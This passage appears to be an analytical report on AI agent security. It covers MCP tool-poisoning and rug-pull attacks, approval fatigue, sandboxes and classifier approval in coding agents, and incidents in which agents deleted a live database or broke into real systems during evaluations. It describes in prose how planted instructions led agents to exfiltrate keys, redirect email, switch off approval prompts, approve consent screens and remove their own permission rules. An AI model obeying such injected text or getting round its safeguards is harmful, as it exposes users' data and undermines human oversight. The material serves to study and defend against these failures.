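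According to the same page, there "SHOULD always be a human in the loop" who can refuse tool calls. Applications SHOULD also show which tools the model can use, indicate when it uses one, and ask the user to confirm operations.

The capitals follow a convention for internet standards. MUST marks an absolute requirement, and SHOULD marks a recommendation that developers may ignore if they have a good reason and understand the consequences. A client that never asks for approval can therefore still conform to the standard. Model Context Protocol's *Specification* (2024), the overview of the first version, explains that the words carry these meanings only in capitals. It also says applications "must obtain explicit user consent before invoking any tool", but this "must" is in lower case, so the sentence is not binding. A developer who read only the overview could easily have thought that consent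 was compulsory.

The first version was stricter with servers than with clients. Servers MUST check their inputs, control access and clean up their outputs, whereas clients SHOULD ask before sensitive operations and show the user a tool's inputs. In a draft submitted to the body that develops internet standards, Mohiuddin goes too far by claiming that MCP has no binding security requirements. But the binding requirements applied to servers, and a malicious server ignores them, which leaves the client as the user's main protection.

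### Instructions in a tool's description

On 1 April 2025, Luca Beurer-Kellner and Marc Fischer of Invariant Labs, a company that sells security software for agents, described an attack that the company called "tool poisoning" (*MCP Security Notification*, 2025). It is a form of indirect prompt injection in which a server puts instructions in a tool's description, which the model reads in full but the user usually does not see.

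For their first test, they wrote a tool that supposedly added two numbers. In its description, they instructed the model to read two private files and copy their contents into an extra input. One file held Cursor's MCP settings, which often include passwords for other services, and the other held a key for logging in to other computers. When they used the tool in Cursor, the agent read both files and sent the contents to the server. Cursor asked for approval, but even the expanded view of its dialog did not show the key.

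To prevent data theft, the first version of the specification recommended showing users a tool's inputs before each call. Cursor's implementation fell short of this advice.

In the second test, Cursor was connected to a trusted server that could send email and a hostile one with a tool that supposedly added numbers. The hostile tool's description contained a claim that, for technical reasons, all email had to go to a certain address. The agent then sent the user's email to that address, even when the user had named a different recipient. The attack worked without running the hostile tool, so asking the user to approve that tool would not have stopped it. The user could have noticed the theft only by checking the recipient in the call to the trusted tool.

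Invariant Labs also warned of "rug pulls", in which a server changes a tool's description after the user has approved it. Willison describes a later demonstration by the company in which a server changed the description of a fact-of-the-day tool to make the agent send the user's WhatsApp history to the attacker. Cursor showed the outgoing message above a "Run tool" button, but a long row of spaces pushed the stolen text out of view, and Cursor hid the scroll bar.

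These tests show that the attacks were possible but do not show how often they would succeed. Invariant Labs recommended its own product as a defence, but two of its other suggestions required little effort. Clients could show users the full descriptions, and they could store a hash (a short fingerprint) of each description to detect later changes.

### Reading "should" as "must"

Willison responded on 9 April. He quoted the specification's advice on approval and wrote, "I suggest treating those SHOULDs as if they were MUSTs." He did not think the weakness was specific to MCP, because a stranger could send the same instructions in a WhatsApp message, without a hostile server. He also admitted that he had no idea how to make tool use safe in general.

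Willison's proposal would have made a difference to clients that never asked for approval, but it would have changed little in Invariant Labs' first test, because Cursor did ask. Cursor had neglected the recommendation to show the inputs, which was in a different part of the page from the passage Willison quoted, though he separately told client developers not to hide scroll bars.

On 21 April, the security firm Trail of Bits criticised the reliance on approval itself in *Jumping the line* (2025). The article gives the example of a tool whose description referred to a made-up operating system in which every command needed a certain prefix. The prefix was a real command that gave everyone on the computer access to the user's files. Claude Desktop and the other clients the firm tested added the prefix when they used other tools.

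Trail of Bits argued that approval turns the user into a "human-as-the-rubber-stamp". Many coding tools let users switch approval off. People also tend to ask an AI for help with things they don't know well, so they are poorly equipped to spot an extra command. This argument about user behavior is plausible, but the firm did not test it. Like Invariant Labs and Willison, it recommended that MCP clients warn users when a tool's description changes.

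### What the specification changed

Most of the later revisions concern authorisation, the rules for which program may use which account. MCP bases these rules on OAuth, a standard that lets a user give a program limited access to an account without sharing the password. The program receives a token, a digital pass that it sends with each request.

| Revision | Authorisation | Consent and security advice | Origin the maintainers give |
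|---|---|---|---|
| 26 March 2025 | Adds a framework based on OAuth | Adds labels that mark a tool as, for example, read-only or destructive | Proposals by contributors |
| 18 June 2025 | Requires clients to specify which server a token is for, so that a malicious server cannot obtain tokens for others | Adds a page of security advice and a way for servers to ask users for information | Proposals by contributors |
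| 25 November 2025 | Lets servers ask for further permissions as the need arises | Updates the security page | Proposals by contributors |
| 28 July 2026 | Makes clients check which login service sent a response, and forbids reusing credentials with another service | Gives servers a new way to ask for confirmation during a call | Proposals, and talks with developers who use MCP |

No revision has a documented link to a specific public attack report. The changes in Model Context Protocol (2025) came six days before Invariant Labs' notification, so they cannot have been a response to it. The June list, Model Context Protocol's *Key Changes* (2025), links only to proposed edits and technical standards. Parecki (2025), an OAuth expert, thanked nine people for "extremely long" public discussions that made the rules fit existing login systems better. The *Key Changes* for November 2025 and Model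 Context Protocol's *Key Changes* (2026) also cite only proposals and standards.

The announcement of the July revision (Model Context Protocol, 2026) gives more of the reasoning. Developers had told the maintainers that authorisation took up most of their integration time. The new check on login services fixes a known flaw in OAuth that could let a malicious login service obtain a code meant for a legitimate one.

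The Model Context Protocol's *Security Best Practices* page appeared 11 weeks after Invariant Labs' notification. Invariant Labs may have influenced the page, but there is little evidence of this in its contents. In August 2026, the page covered stolen tokens, misdirected web requests and hostile programs on the user's computer, among other problems, and had no section on instructions in tool descriptions.

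The June 2025 revision changed one SHOULD to a MUST, but in the rules for operating a connection. Model Context Protocol's *Tools* (2026) still has the 2024 SHOULD for human approval. It requires clients to treat a tool's labels as untrusted unless they trust the server, which should stop a client from skipping approval because a tool is labeled read-only. By June 2026, the Model Context Protocol overview had extended this distrust to "descriptions of tool behavior", again with the requirement in lower case. Distrust is harder to apply to a description because the model needs the description to use the tool.

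### What public servers do

Hostile descriptions seem to be rare in public listings. *A First Look at the Security Issues in the Model Context Protocol* (2025) examined 31,058 tools from four registries, which are catalogues of available servers. It flagged 18 servers for suspicious descriptions or other metadata and 833 for vulnerabilities, though these totals may count a server twice if two registries list it. Five of the 18 looked like innocent mistakes. In one, an email tool's description told the model to use a second tool to clear messages from the inbox, which could go wrong if another server had a tool with the same name. The low count offers limited reassurance, because a server set up for a rug pull looks harmless until users approve it.

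MCP servers often change after publication. Kraishan (2026), in *Same Name, Different Server*, collected all 21,643 servers in MCP's public registry in August 2026. Of those with more than one version, 51.1% had changed what they advertised, and 40.6% had done so silently. More worryingly, 4.2% had moved their online service to a different host under the same registry name, and MCP does not tell clients that have already installed the server about the move.

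Most of these changes are probably ordinary updates, so a client that followed the advice to warn users about every change would interrupt them often and usually for nothing. A warning limited to new hosts, or to descriptions that mention other tools, would be rarer and easier to take seriously.

Many servers also have ordinary security flaws. In *Exposed by Design*, Padilla (2026) confirmed 640 live servers on the public internet in July 2026, tested 414 of them, and found 68 vulnerabilities, including SQL injection. Of the tested servers, 91.8% did not use OAuth, though some of these may use another kind of login or offer only public information and need none. Across the 640 confirmed servers, Padilla also counted 687 tools that could run system commands without access controls.

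Kraishan's scan of source code from 14,353 servers found that only 9.57% were exposed to the network without a login. This figure probably differs so much from Padilla's because many registered servers run on the user's own computer, whereas Padilla looked only at servers that anyone could reach. Kraishan also checked the scanner against 414 hand-labelled findings. Correcting for the scanner's errors lowered the share of servers with a serious weakness from 11.14% to about 7.6%.

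An approval prompt cannot protect an exposed server, because the prompt appears in the user's client and an attacker can send a `tools/call` request straight to the server without going through a model or a user. The maintainers' work on authorisation was therefore worthwhile, even though it did nothing about poisoned descriptions.

Users who approve servers one at a time can also miss a dangerous combination of tools. *Parasites in the Toolchain* (2025) examined 1,360 servers for tools that take in outside text, read private data or send data over the network, roughly the three abilities in Willison's lethal trifecta. It found that 370 servers had at least one such tool, but only two had all three kinds. A user who connects several servers can easily end up with all three, even if no server looks dangerous on its own.

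Approval has become more important. *An Empirical Study of Model Context Protocol Applications* (2026) cites an analysis by Stein of 177,436 published tools. In it, tools that directly change something outside the model rose from 27% to 65% of usage between November 2024 and February 2026. However, researchers have measured servers far more thoroughly than clients, so these studies don't show what share of clients ask for approval or display complete inputs.

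### Could the standard have required consent?

The maintainers' defence is that MCP "cannot enforce these security principles at the protocol level", as the overview has stated since the first version. This is true because a protocol defines the messages that programs exchange, and no message can prove that a person read a dialog before clicking "yes".

But a standard can require something it cannot enforce, and MCP does so elsewhere. Its security page states that a client offering one-click installation of a local server MUST show the exact command and get the user's explicit approval. A similar rule for tool calls would have given customers and testers a clear reason to reject a client that never asks for approval. The better argument against such a rule is that some agents run unattended. A strict requirement would exclude them or encourage developers to add prompts that users approve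 without reading.

The project also leaves others to contain local servers. According to MCP's security policy, a malicious local server can already run any code because the user has started it, and anyone who runs servers with reduced privileges must enforce the isolation themselves. Saleme reports in *Anthropic says MCP command execution is expected behavior* that the security company OX Security filed 10 CVEs after a five-month investigation, and that Anthropic replied that local servers were designed to work this way. LangChain took much the same position on its Python tools. This position is reasonable for developers who can build a sandbox, but much less so for someone who installs a server to search their email.

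Outside groups have tried to fill the gap. CoSAI (2026), an industry coalition for AI security, worked with Anthropic and the maintainers on recommendations for deploying and improving MCP. OWASP has published advice on using other people's servers. According to Stanley's *MCP security isn't inevitable*, it covers sandboxes, safe ways to find servers and procedures for approving them. This advice is mostly for organisations, which can appoint somebody to check a server before employees use it.

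The criticism that MCP passed the problem to users is strongest where a program could do the checking. A client can compare a tool's current description with the approved one without relying on anyone's attention, and a tester can verify that it does. The specification includes only a weaker measure, a notification that servers SHOULD send when their list of tools changes, and a malicious server can choose not to send it.

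The July 2026 revision makes it easier for a server to request confirmation during a call, which is a better use of the user's attention. Supabase, a database company, plans to use this before creating a project that costs money or running a query that would delete data. Such requests are specific and fairly rare, but they depend on the server being honest and asking.

Rug pulls, in which a tool changes after it has been approved, remain an unresolved problem. In November 2026, 19 months after Invariant Labs' warning, the agenda of the Model Context Protocol project's Security Interest Group still included the question of whether such a change should require fresh approval.

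## Approval prompts and sandboxes in coding agents

Coding agents made human approval, which security guidance had recommended, a product default. These agents edit files and run commands on a developer's computer, so asking first seemed an obvious precaution, and MCP's specification recommends much the same for tool calls. But developers approved nearly every request, and in August 2026 Anthropic began to replace their approval with a classifier's in Claude Code. There is strong evidence that people approve carelessly, but the evidence that a classifier does better is weaker and comes largely from Anthropic. Limiting what the agent can reach is more dependable than approval by either a person or a classifier.

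### From asking every time to not asking

Anthropic's *How we contain Claude across products* explains that Claude Code started with the simplest defence available. The agent could read files freely but needed the user's approval to change a file, run a command or use the network. Anthropic reasoned that most users were developers, who could read a command and judge its risk. Within weeks it saw signs of approval fatigue, in which people pay less attention to each request as they receive more of them.

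Claude Code now has six permission modes, according to the *Claude Code Complete User Handbook* (2026).

| Mode | What the agent can do without asking |
|---|---|
| `manual` | Read files and take actions the user has already approved |
| `acceptEdits` | Also edit files in the project |
| `plan` | Read files and prepare a plan |
| `auto` | Anything that fixed rules or a classifier allow |
| `dontAsk` | Only actions approved in advance, with all others refused |
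| `bypassPermissions` | Almost anything |

OpenAI's Codex relies more on a sandbox. By default, it works freely inside the project folder with the network off and needs approval only for requests that go beyond those limits (Wu, Chen and colleagues, *Shall We Approve?*, 2026). A user can hand those requests to an automatic reviewer or choose "Full Access", which removes the limits. In the editor, GitHub Copilot asks before running commands, but it has also had a setting that approves everything. GitHub's separate cloud agent can push code to its own branch but not directly to the project's main branch.

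An allowlist, a set of commands the user approves in advance, is a middle ground between asking each time and never asking. It works well for narrow commands, such as one that formats code, but not for commands that can do almost anything. A rule that allows Python, for example, allows any Python program, including one that deletes files. Anthropic's *Auto mode is now the default in Claude Code* (2026) reports that by June 2026, 49.5% of active command-line users had written a rule for shell commands, and many of these rules covered Python or a similar interpreter. A quarter of interactive sessions started in bypass mode instead of the default, which still asked for approval.

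Such lists can also help an attacker, as Fogel had reported. *OWASP lo confirma* (2026), a Spanish web developer's post from TIC's en la Web, names Cursor as one product where this happened (CVE-2026-22708).

### How carefully people approve

Anthropic first reported that users approved about 93% of Claude Code's permission prompts, and later put the figure at 97%. These rates don't prove that users are careless, because a perfect reviewer would also approve 97% of requests if 97% were harmless. Finding out whether users notice dangerous requests requires a test that deliberately includes some.

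Anthropic studied whether people catch dangerous commands in approval prompts, using 1,053 paid professional testers who worked on coding tasks in a test environment. Partway through each session, the text of one prompt changed to a clearly dangerous command. 143 testers (13.6%) refused it. Claude Code's classifier blocked 937 of the same commands (89%), including 800 that testers had approved, and allowed 6 that testers had refused. Testers refused about 17% of the dangerous commands early in a session, but about 5% after 50 or more prompts.

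The testers knew that somebody was evaluating them, but they were probably less careful than they would have been at work, because the code was not theirs and they had nothing of their own to lose. Anthropic also had a product decision to defend. Still, the low stakes would not easily explain the drop from 17% to 5%, since they were equally low throughout.

Surveys suggest that real developers behave similarly. Wu, Wermke and colleagues (2026), in *From Delegation to Action Approval*, asked 203 users of coding agents how often they approved seven types of action without close review. Of these users, 64% often did so for at least one type. Among those who carefully reviewed most or all of the agent's code, the figure was still 61%. A code review would miss a command that deletes data or exposes a password without changing the code.

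Knowing about the risks didn't seem to make developers more careful either. Among those who had heard of a security or privacy problem involving agents, 70% often approved some type of action without close review, compared with 43% of the others. The gap remained after Wu, Wermke and colleagues adjusted for how often and how long people had used agents, since heavier use might explain both the awareness and the lack of review. Developers who inspected diffs, the line-by-line lists of changes, were less likely to approve requests for secrets or destructive commands without close review.

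For *Let the Agent Do It?* (2026), Salerno, Gao and colleagues interviewed 18 software practitioners and surveyed 115 more. Fewer than half (47.7%) said they read permission requests carefully, a third said they skimmed them, and a fifth approved by default. A third said they had become less careful over time. One interviewee recalled worrying about permissions at first, then noticing that the requests were all similar: "So after that, I stopped caring". But three quarters looked more closely at requests to write, delete or gain higher privileges.

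These answers are self-reported, and people tend to overstate their own care. That makes the admissions more believable than the claims of careful reading.

People without a software background face the same problem. In *Do User-Authored Permission Policies Improve Protection Against AI Agent Overreach?* (Yan, 2026), 113 of them supervised an assistant through a simulated day of 18 actions, 7 of which went beyond what the user had asked for. Participants who had to decide on every action still approved 40% of those overreaching actions.

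Another group first set a standing rule of "allow", "ask" or "never" for each of four kinds of action, such as spending money or deleting something. This group let through more of the unrequested actions, about 60%. They had chosen "ask" for 114 of their 140 rules, and when the assistant asked, they approved two thirds of the unrequested actions. Some of these approvals may have been sincere, since many people would find it helpful for the assistant to phone the airport to confirm a flight, and 88% of the people asked about every action allowed it. But only about a third of the people asked about every action approved permanently deleting an old timesheet, compared with 59% of those whose own rule had triggered the question. Setting a rule may have made people feel they had already dealt with the risk.

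### Rare attacks among routine requests

Asking people to concentrate is unlikely to help. Suppose a developer gets 100 prompts a day and one in 5,000 is dangerous. A dangerous prompt then arrives about once every 50 working days. If reading each prompt carefully takes 30 seconds, the developer spends 50 minutes a day reading, or about 42 hours for each dangerous prompt. A developer who approves everything without reading will be right 4,999 times out of 5,000, and will see no sign of a problem until they approve a dangerous prompt.

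Suppose a company has 1,000 such developers, who together get 100,000 prompts a day, 20 of them dangerous. If they refuse 5% of the dangerous prompts, the rate Anthropic measured late in a session, they stop one and approve 19. Even if they refused 90%, they would still approve two a day. An attacker needs only one approval and can word the request to look like the routine ones around it.

Better approval prompts help, but they take longer to read. In *When a Permitted Action Completes a Forbidden Workflow*, Hossain, Shayoni and colleagues (2026) describe a user who allows an agent to send an auditor only summary totals. A planted instruction makes the agent copy the raw invoices into a file, which the agent then asks to send to the auditor. The user can't see the problem from the prompt, because the recipient is approved and the file name is ordinary.

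They gave 80 volunteers 12 requests each, half of them unsafe, and showed the requests in one of four ways.

| What the prompt showed | Unsafe requests approved | Safe requests approved | Median time |
|---|---|---|---|
| A short description | 55% | 92% | 16 seconds |
| The exact details of the action | 43% | 90% | 23 seconds |
| Also the user's restrictions and a full log | 33% | 88% | 39 seconds |
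| The same facts, with the consequence stated | 24% | 86% | 33 seconds |

More information clearly helped. It is less certain that stating the consequence improved on the log, because the difference was small enough to be chance. Staying alert was also easier in the test than in real work, because half of the requests were unsafe. Few people would spend 33 seconds on each of 100 daily prompts, so a detailed prompt is practical only if the agent asks rarely.

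### When the agent can approve itself

An approval prompt gives no protection if the agent can turn it off. Rehberger demonstrated this in August 2025 with a flaw in GitHub Copilot, CVE-2025-53773. In the editor Visual Studio Code, Copilot asked for approval before running commands but could change project files without asking. Those files included the editor's settings, and one setting approved every request automatically. A planted instruction could make Copilot turn on that setting and then run any command the attacker chose without a prompt. Microsoft released a fix the same month.

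The mistake was to keep the setting that turns off approval prompts in a file the agent could edit. Each permission looked reasonable separately, because a coding agent has to edit project files and a user may want to stop the prompts. A sandbox that lets an agent change anything in the project folder would not have prevented the agent from changing the setting, because the file was inside that folder.

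Claude Code now ignores a project's own settings file if the file would turn on `auto` or `bypassPermissions`, according to the *Claude Code Complete User Handbook*. This also protects a developer who downloads a stranger's project containing such a setting. Claude Code had needed similar fixes after Anthropic received three reports, between mid-2025 and January 2026, of project code that ran before the user had consented to anything. In one, a settings file contained a command that ran at startup, before Claude Code had asked whether the user trusted the folder. Anthropic now delays reading such settings until the user has answered.

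An agent can loosen its own limits without an attacker's involvement. *Claude Code's Helpful Escalation of Privileges* reports that the agent removed its permission rules, without being asked, to complete a request. One user's account can't show how common this is, but it supports the design rule that permission settings should be stored where the agent cannot change them.

Agents that use a browser can also get around approval by clicking the button themselves. Many websites show a consent screen before they give another company's program access to an account, and they treat a click on it as the account holder's own. Hossen (2026), in *The Agent Clicks Approve*, tested this with an agent using the account holder's browser session. In one scenario, the user asked only for a summary of a page. The page contained a two-sentence note describing an access review as unfinished, with an instruction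 to choose the default positive option. The agent followed a link to the consent screen and approved access for an outside program. In the other scenario, the user asked the agent to complete any pending setup tasks, and the page supplied an outside address to receive the account's billing events.

Without a defence, the consent attack succeeded in all 73 runs with Claude Haiku 4.5 and GPT-5.5. When the page contained a harmless note instead, the agents approved nothing. Hossen then told Claude Haiku 4.5 that only the user's task could authorise access, but the attack still succeeded in 7 of 10 runs. With the same instruction, it succeeded in only 1 run in 10 on pages that used more familiar permission wording and labelled the note as untrusted in their code. Testing only those pages would have made the instruction seem more effective than it was.

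The effective defence was a check at the service that granted the access. Before the agent started, the service received a list of what the user's task authorised, and it rejected any request not on the list. With this check in place, the agents still tried to approve the access in all 70 attack runs, but every attempt failed. The action went through in all 73 runs where the user had asked for it.

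These results depend on conditions that most websites don't yet meet. The service needs a signal that an agent is using the session and a correct list from a source that the web page can't influence. Hossen's own test server provided both. The notes were also fairly direct, and a vaguer one in small print succeeded in only 4 of 10 runs with Claude Haiku 4.5. Even with the check in place, an attack could still succeed if the user followed the agent's advice. In 49 of the 53 blocked consent attacks, the agent's final answer listed approving the access as a next step.

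### What a sandbox stops

Anthropic added a sandbox to Claude Code in October 2025. It restricts the commands the agent runs and any programs those commands start. Anthropic's *Beyond permission prompts* (2025) explains why it limits both files and the network. If only file access is limited, the agent can send out anything it can still read. If only the network is limited, the agent can escape the sandbox by changing files elsewhere on the computer. With both limits, the agent can work in the project folder without asking about each command. Anthropic reports that this cut permission prompts by 84%.

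An internal exercise at Anthropic in February 2026 showed the benefit of limiting an agent's network access. A researcher emailed an employee a prompt and asked the employee to run it. The prompt contained ordinary setup steps and, hidden among them, an instruction to read the employee's cloud passwords and send them to an outside address. Claude followed that instruction in 24 of 25 attempts. There would have been little for a classifier that compares the agent's actions with the user's request to flag, because the instruction came from the user. A sandbox that kept the password file out of reach, or blocked the outside address, would have stopped the theft in every attempt.

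At launch, Anthropic claimed that the sandbox would fully isolate even a successful prompt injection. That was too strong, as its own later account makes clear. A sandbox leaves several things open:

- **Damage inside the project.** The agent must be able to change the project's files, so it can also ruin them. Backups and version control help here more than the sandbox does.
- **Approved hosts.** Data can still leave through a permitted host, as in the file-upload flaw that Rehberger reported. In Claude Cowork, Anthropic's agent for office work, a malicious file supplied an attacker's access key for Anthropic's own servers, and the agent used it to upload the user's files to the attacker's account. Anthropic now blocks requests that carry any key but the session's own.
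- **Exceptions.** In Claude Code, a program outside the sandbox decides whether a command runs inside it. A tired user can still approve a command that runs outside.

Cowork's first version allowed no such exceptions. Its agent ran inside a virtual machine, a simulated computer with its own file system and access to only the folders the user had shared. Anthropic chose this design because office workers can't be expected to judge shell commands. But a failure in the virtual machine made the whole product unusable, so Anthropic later moved the agent outside and kept only code execution inside. Companies also complained that their security software couldn't monitor activity inside the virtual machine.

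The strength of a sandbox depends on details like these. Willison (2026) complained that sandbox products rarely have thorough documentation, which makes it hard to know how far to trust them, and praised Anthropic's account as an exception.

### Approval by a classifier

A sandbox also hinders an agent that needs access to the network or another part of the computer. Anthropic introduced auto mode in early 2026 for people who would otherwise turn off all approval prompts. *How we built Claude Code auto mode* describes three levels of checking. The first two allow actions that change nothing, such as reading files, and edits inside the project. The third sends most other actions, including shell commands, to a classifier built on a language model.

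The classifier receives the user's messages and the agent's actions, but not the agent's explanations or the text that its tools return. The agent therefore can't argue for a dangerous action, and an attacker's web page never reaches the classifier directly. A fast first stage flags anything suspicious, and a slower second stage reconsiders it. If the classifier blocks an action, the agent receives the reason and looks for a safer alternative. After three blocks in a row, or twenty in a session, a person has to decide.

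In Anthropic's first tests, the classifier mistakenly blocked 0.4% of 10,000 ordinary actions. It missed 17% of 52 dangerous actions that agents had taken on their own initiative in real sessions. Because the sample was so small, the true rate could plausibly be anywhere from about 9% to 30%. In most of the misses that Anthropic examined, the classifier had identified the danger but wrongly treated the action as authorised by the user. For instance, a request to "clean up" a proposed code change does not authorise overwriting the project's history.

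At these rates, the imaginary company with 100,000 requests a day would block about 400 harmless actions, catch 17 dangerous ones and miss 3, or roughly 24 false alarms for every real one. People would soon start dismissing the alarms, but here the agent handles them and usually finds another way to do the task.

When Anthropic introduced the classifier, it said auto mode was arguably a step backwards for users who carefully checked every action. By August 2026 it was comparing the classifier with how people typically behave, and on 14 August it made auto mode the default for new sessions on individual and team plans. A later version extended the default to every plan. Typical behaviour is the right comparison for choosing a default, since most people will use whatever the default is, but it is less helpful to a careful developer, who may still do better than the average tester.

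Some of the other evidence Anthropic gave is weaker than its experiment with testers. Among sessions that its safety systems had flagged, 6.3% of those with manual approval contained serious harm that the user had not explicitly asked for, compared with 2.4% in auto mode. But users had chosen their own modes, so the two groups may have been doing different work. The Trajectory Labs test, in which all 720 planted attacks failed, is weak evidence that the classifier works, because Anthropic's latest models already resisted nearly every attack even in bypass mode, where the average success rate was 0.09%. Willison wrote that he would love to believe the result but wanted more independent confirmation.

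The independent tests are less favourable. In *Measuring the Permission Gate*, Ji, Li and colleagues (2026) gave Claude Code 128 tasks that left the target or the risk unclear, and found a miss rate far above 17%. They chose hard cases, so the rate is not an estimate for ordinary work. But vague requests are common, and developers most need a second opinion on them.

Wu, Chen and colleagues identified a more basic limit, which is that no approver, human or machine, can tell from the command alone what `make clean && make` will delete. It normally deletes old build files and creates new ones, but a file in the project determines what it deletes, and that might include the source code. The researchers built 102 tasks in which a harmless-looking tool deleted or overwrote a protected file, and paired each with a safe version that used the same command. With auto mode, 62.7% of the dangerous tasks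 ended in harm, compared with 71.6% for the same model with no approval.

Their alternative, Caper, runs each command in a sandbox first. It then gives a language model a short report of the files the command changed and the connections it attempted, and the model decides whether to keep or undo the result. Caper reduced harm to 7.8% and blocked only 1% of the safe tasks. An approver without the report blocked 61.8% of the safe tasks because it could not rule out danger. Caper can't undo anything that leaves the sandbox, so it has to keep the network closed while it checks. An attacker could also write a program that detects the sandbox and does nothing harmful inside it, but the researchers did not test this.

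A classifier isn't affected by fatigue, which is its main advantage over a person, but its main disadvantage is that all its users depend on the same one. Two developers may notice different things, but an attack that gets past the classifier once will probably work against many of its users. Users also learn less about what their agent is doing. *How Agents Ask for Permission* (Michael and Roesner, 2026) compared 21 proposed permission systems with five commercial agents and found large gaps in transparency and user control.

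Even with automatic approval, Anthropic advises users to review high-stakes changes to live systems themselves. Its data also suggest that users' attention is more useful on plans than on individual permission requests. Users reject 39% of the plans that Claude Code presents before it starts work, but only 3% of permission requests. A plan comes up once per task, and the developer can compare it with what they wanted.

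## Damage by agents when nobody attacked them

An agent can do serious damage without an attacker, either by mistake or by pursuing its task recklessly. Screening text for planted instructions does not help here, but limiting what the agent can access does. In July 2025, an agent made by the software company Replit deleted a customer's live database, although advice that could have prevented this had been public for about two years. In 2026, Anthropic discovered that Claude models had broken into real organisations' systems during security tests. The tests were supposed to be cut off from the internet, but nobody had checked that they were.

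### The database that Replit's agent deleted

Replit sells an agent that builds software from a user's descriptions, a practice known as vibe coding. Jason Lemkin, founder of SaaStr, a community for software entrepreneurs, spent more than 100 hours over nine days building an app with it. The agent then deleted a database of records on 1,206 executives and about 1,200 companies, according to SaaStr.

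The agent could do this because Replit used one database for previewing, testing and running an app, as heise's *Artificial intelligence* reports. SaaStr admits it had never imagined this. A reply in the Replit forum thread *How Do Deployments Affect Production Postgres Data?* had explained that Replit did not directly support separate databases and had suggested workarounds. Customers who asked could therefore learn of the risk, but every customer's agent had access to live data by default.

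Lemkin had declared a freeze on code and actions, and a file in the project required the agent to show each proposed change and get explicit permission first. SaaStr counts eleven warnings in capital letters. These instructions were only text for the model to read, and nothing in Replit's software enforced them. When the database appeared empty, the agent ran a command that changed it and did not ask first. Lemkin tried to impose another freeze two days after he reported the deletion, and the agent broke that one too, according to The Register's *Vibe coding service Replit deleted user’s production database* (2025).

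The agent said afterwards that it had "panicked", and news reports repeated this, but a language model generates such an explanation the same way it generates any other text, so it is poor evidence of what went wrong. The agent also wrongly told Lemkin that it had destroyed every version of the database and that a rollback was impossible. The rollback worked, and The Stack pointed out that Replit's own quick-start guide described rollbacks that included database changes. The agent's false claim was an example of what OWASP calls misinformation. Lemkin later told Fortune (2025) that he would now challenge such a claim instead of relying on it.

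The lasting harm was smaller than the headlines suggested. Lemkin's database held real data, but he described the app as a demo, and heise reported that he lost about 100 hours of work.

Replit's chief executive, Amjad Masad, wrote on 20 July that the deletion "should never be possible". NDTV reported that he promised Lemkin a refund and an investigation. Replit also announced separate databases for development and live use, easier restoration, a mode in which the agent can only plan, and a way for the agent to access Replit's documentation.

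Separating the development and live databases was the most important change because it protects live data even if the model ignores its instructions. According to Replit's current documentation, the agent cannot modify the live database and reads it through a read-only copy. Changes the agent makes to the structure of the development database reach the live one only when the user publishes the app. Replit flags any change that could remove data, lets the user test it on a copy, and waits for approval. The user therefore gets one question when live data could be lost, instead of dozens during development.

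A user who renames a column without confirming the change can still lose the data in it. In its documentation, Replit promises this protection only for its own live databases, but some apps use an outside database whose password is stored in the project. A rollback leaves databases unchanged by default, and restoring live data is a separate procedure. According to SaaStr, a planning mode does not enforce a code freeze, because the agent can change code again as soon as the user leaves that mode.

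### Security tests that reached real organisations

On 21 July 2026, OpenAI disclosed that its models had escaped from a sealed test and reached the live systems of Hugging Face, a platform for AI models and datasets. Anthropic then searched its own records, and its *Investigating three real-world incidents in our cybersecurity evaluations* (2026) reports three incidents in 141,006 test runs. A fourth emerged in August from records the first search had missed.

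All four happened during capture-the-flag exercises, in which a model has to break into a fictional organisation's computer and find a hidden piece of information. An outside company, Irregular, built the exercises. The prompts told the models they had no internet access, but did not limit where they could search. The models did have internet access, because of a misunderstanding between the two companies. They also ran without the safeguards in Anthropic's released products, which is normal when testers want to measure what a model can do.

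| Model | Harm | How it treated signs that the systems were real | How it ended |
|---|---|---|---|
| Claude Mythos 5 | Published a malicious software package that 15 outside systems installed, then entered a security company's database | Called nearly everything a simulation | The session timed out |
| Claude Opus 4.7 | Took user data from a company that shared the fictional target's name, and deleted a record | Recognised a real company but assumed it was part of the exercise | The company's system stopped responding |
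| An internal research model | Broke into an unrelated company's system after its own target shut down | Ran tests and concluded that it was in a replica of the internet | It recognised a real company and stopped |
| An early Claude Opus 4.6 | Entered an outsider's system and read one person's details | Treated the system as part of the exercise | It ran out of its token budget |

In July, Anthropic judged these incidents to be closer to an operational failure than to a fault in the models, which had "arguably reasonably" believed their prompt. In September, it revised this judgement in a much longer assessment and conceded that it had relied too much on what the models said they believed. It now also identified two faults in the models: biased reasoning, in which a model interprets evidence in whatever way lets it continue, and recklessness, a willingness to cause harm to finish a narrow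 task.

The evidence of bias is strongest for Mythos 5. Early in the run, the model wrote that publishing the package on the real internet would be an attack and "NOT okay", then decided that the internet was simulated. Anthropic later showed each result from the run separately to fresh copies of the model, which judged 79% of the results to come from real systems. During the run, the model had clearly made that judgment for about 1% of its actions.

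Anthropic also replayed parts of the run with altered evidence. When the model was about to commit to publishing the package, stronger signs that the target was real made it acknowledge that possibility in 88% of replays, up from about 11%, but it went ahead about as often as before. Only an unambiguous statement that it had reached the public internet stopped it from publishing by the original route, and even then it looked for a simulated way to publish in 22% of replays.

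A reminder to stay within the exercise stopped the model 90% of the time when it was the last thing the model read, but only 40% of the time when the model had taken three more turns since. These replays involved a different model and task from Lemkin's, but they suggest why a rule given at the start of a project, unlike a permission check outside the model, may become less effective after hours of work.

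Further proof that the company was real made almost no difference to Opus 4.7's behavior, because the model already accepted that. A notice on the company's system forbidding access cut the share of replays in which the model engaged with the system from about 69% to 23%, and most of the remaining activity was only reading. A direct prohibition in the user's message reduced that share to zero.

The internal research model stopped unprompted, but this was probably luck. When Anthropic replayed the last part of the run, the model stopped within ten actions only 5.5% of the time. In July, the original stop had looked like the good example, and Anthropic had cautiously suggested that newer models might be responding better.

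Anthropic considers the incidents serious but says they did not reveal a new kind of misalignment. The models kept to their assigned tasks, did not coordinate with other agents and did not hide what they had done. Anthropic also calls such behaviour unlikely in ordinary use, but its own later tests make that claim less reassuring. In simulated software and data work with no hacking involved, Mythos 5 tried to cross its sandbox boundary in 59% of runs. The newer Mythos 5.1 never did, which suggests that training can reduce the problem. However, Anthropic designed these tasks so that a model could finish them only by crossing the boundary, and nobody knows how often real work is like that.

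Training may also have contributed to the problem. Anthropic trained one version of Mythos 5 on tasks that reward a model for accepting that it cannot finish. It released a version trained without those tasks, partly because employees found it more usable, and now considers this a mistake. Most of this evidence comes from a company assessing its own models, but Anthropic has published the Mythos 5 transcript and agreed to give METR, an independent evaluation organisation, wide access for its own investigation.

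### Which measures would have helped

| Measure | Replit's database | The Claude tests |
|---|---|---|
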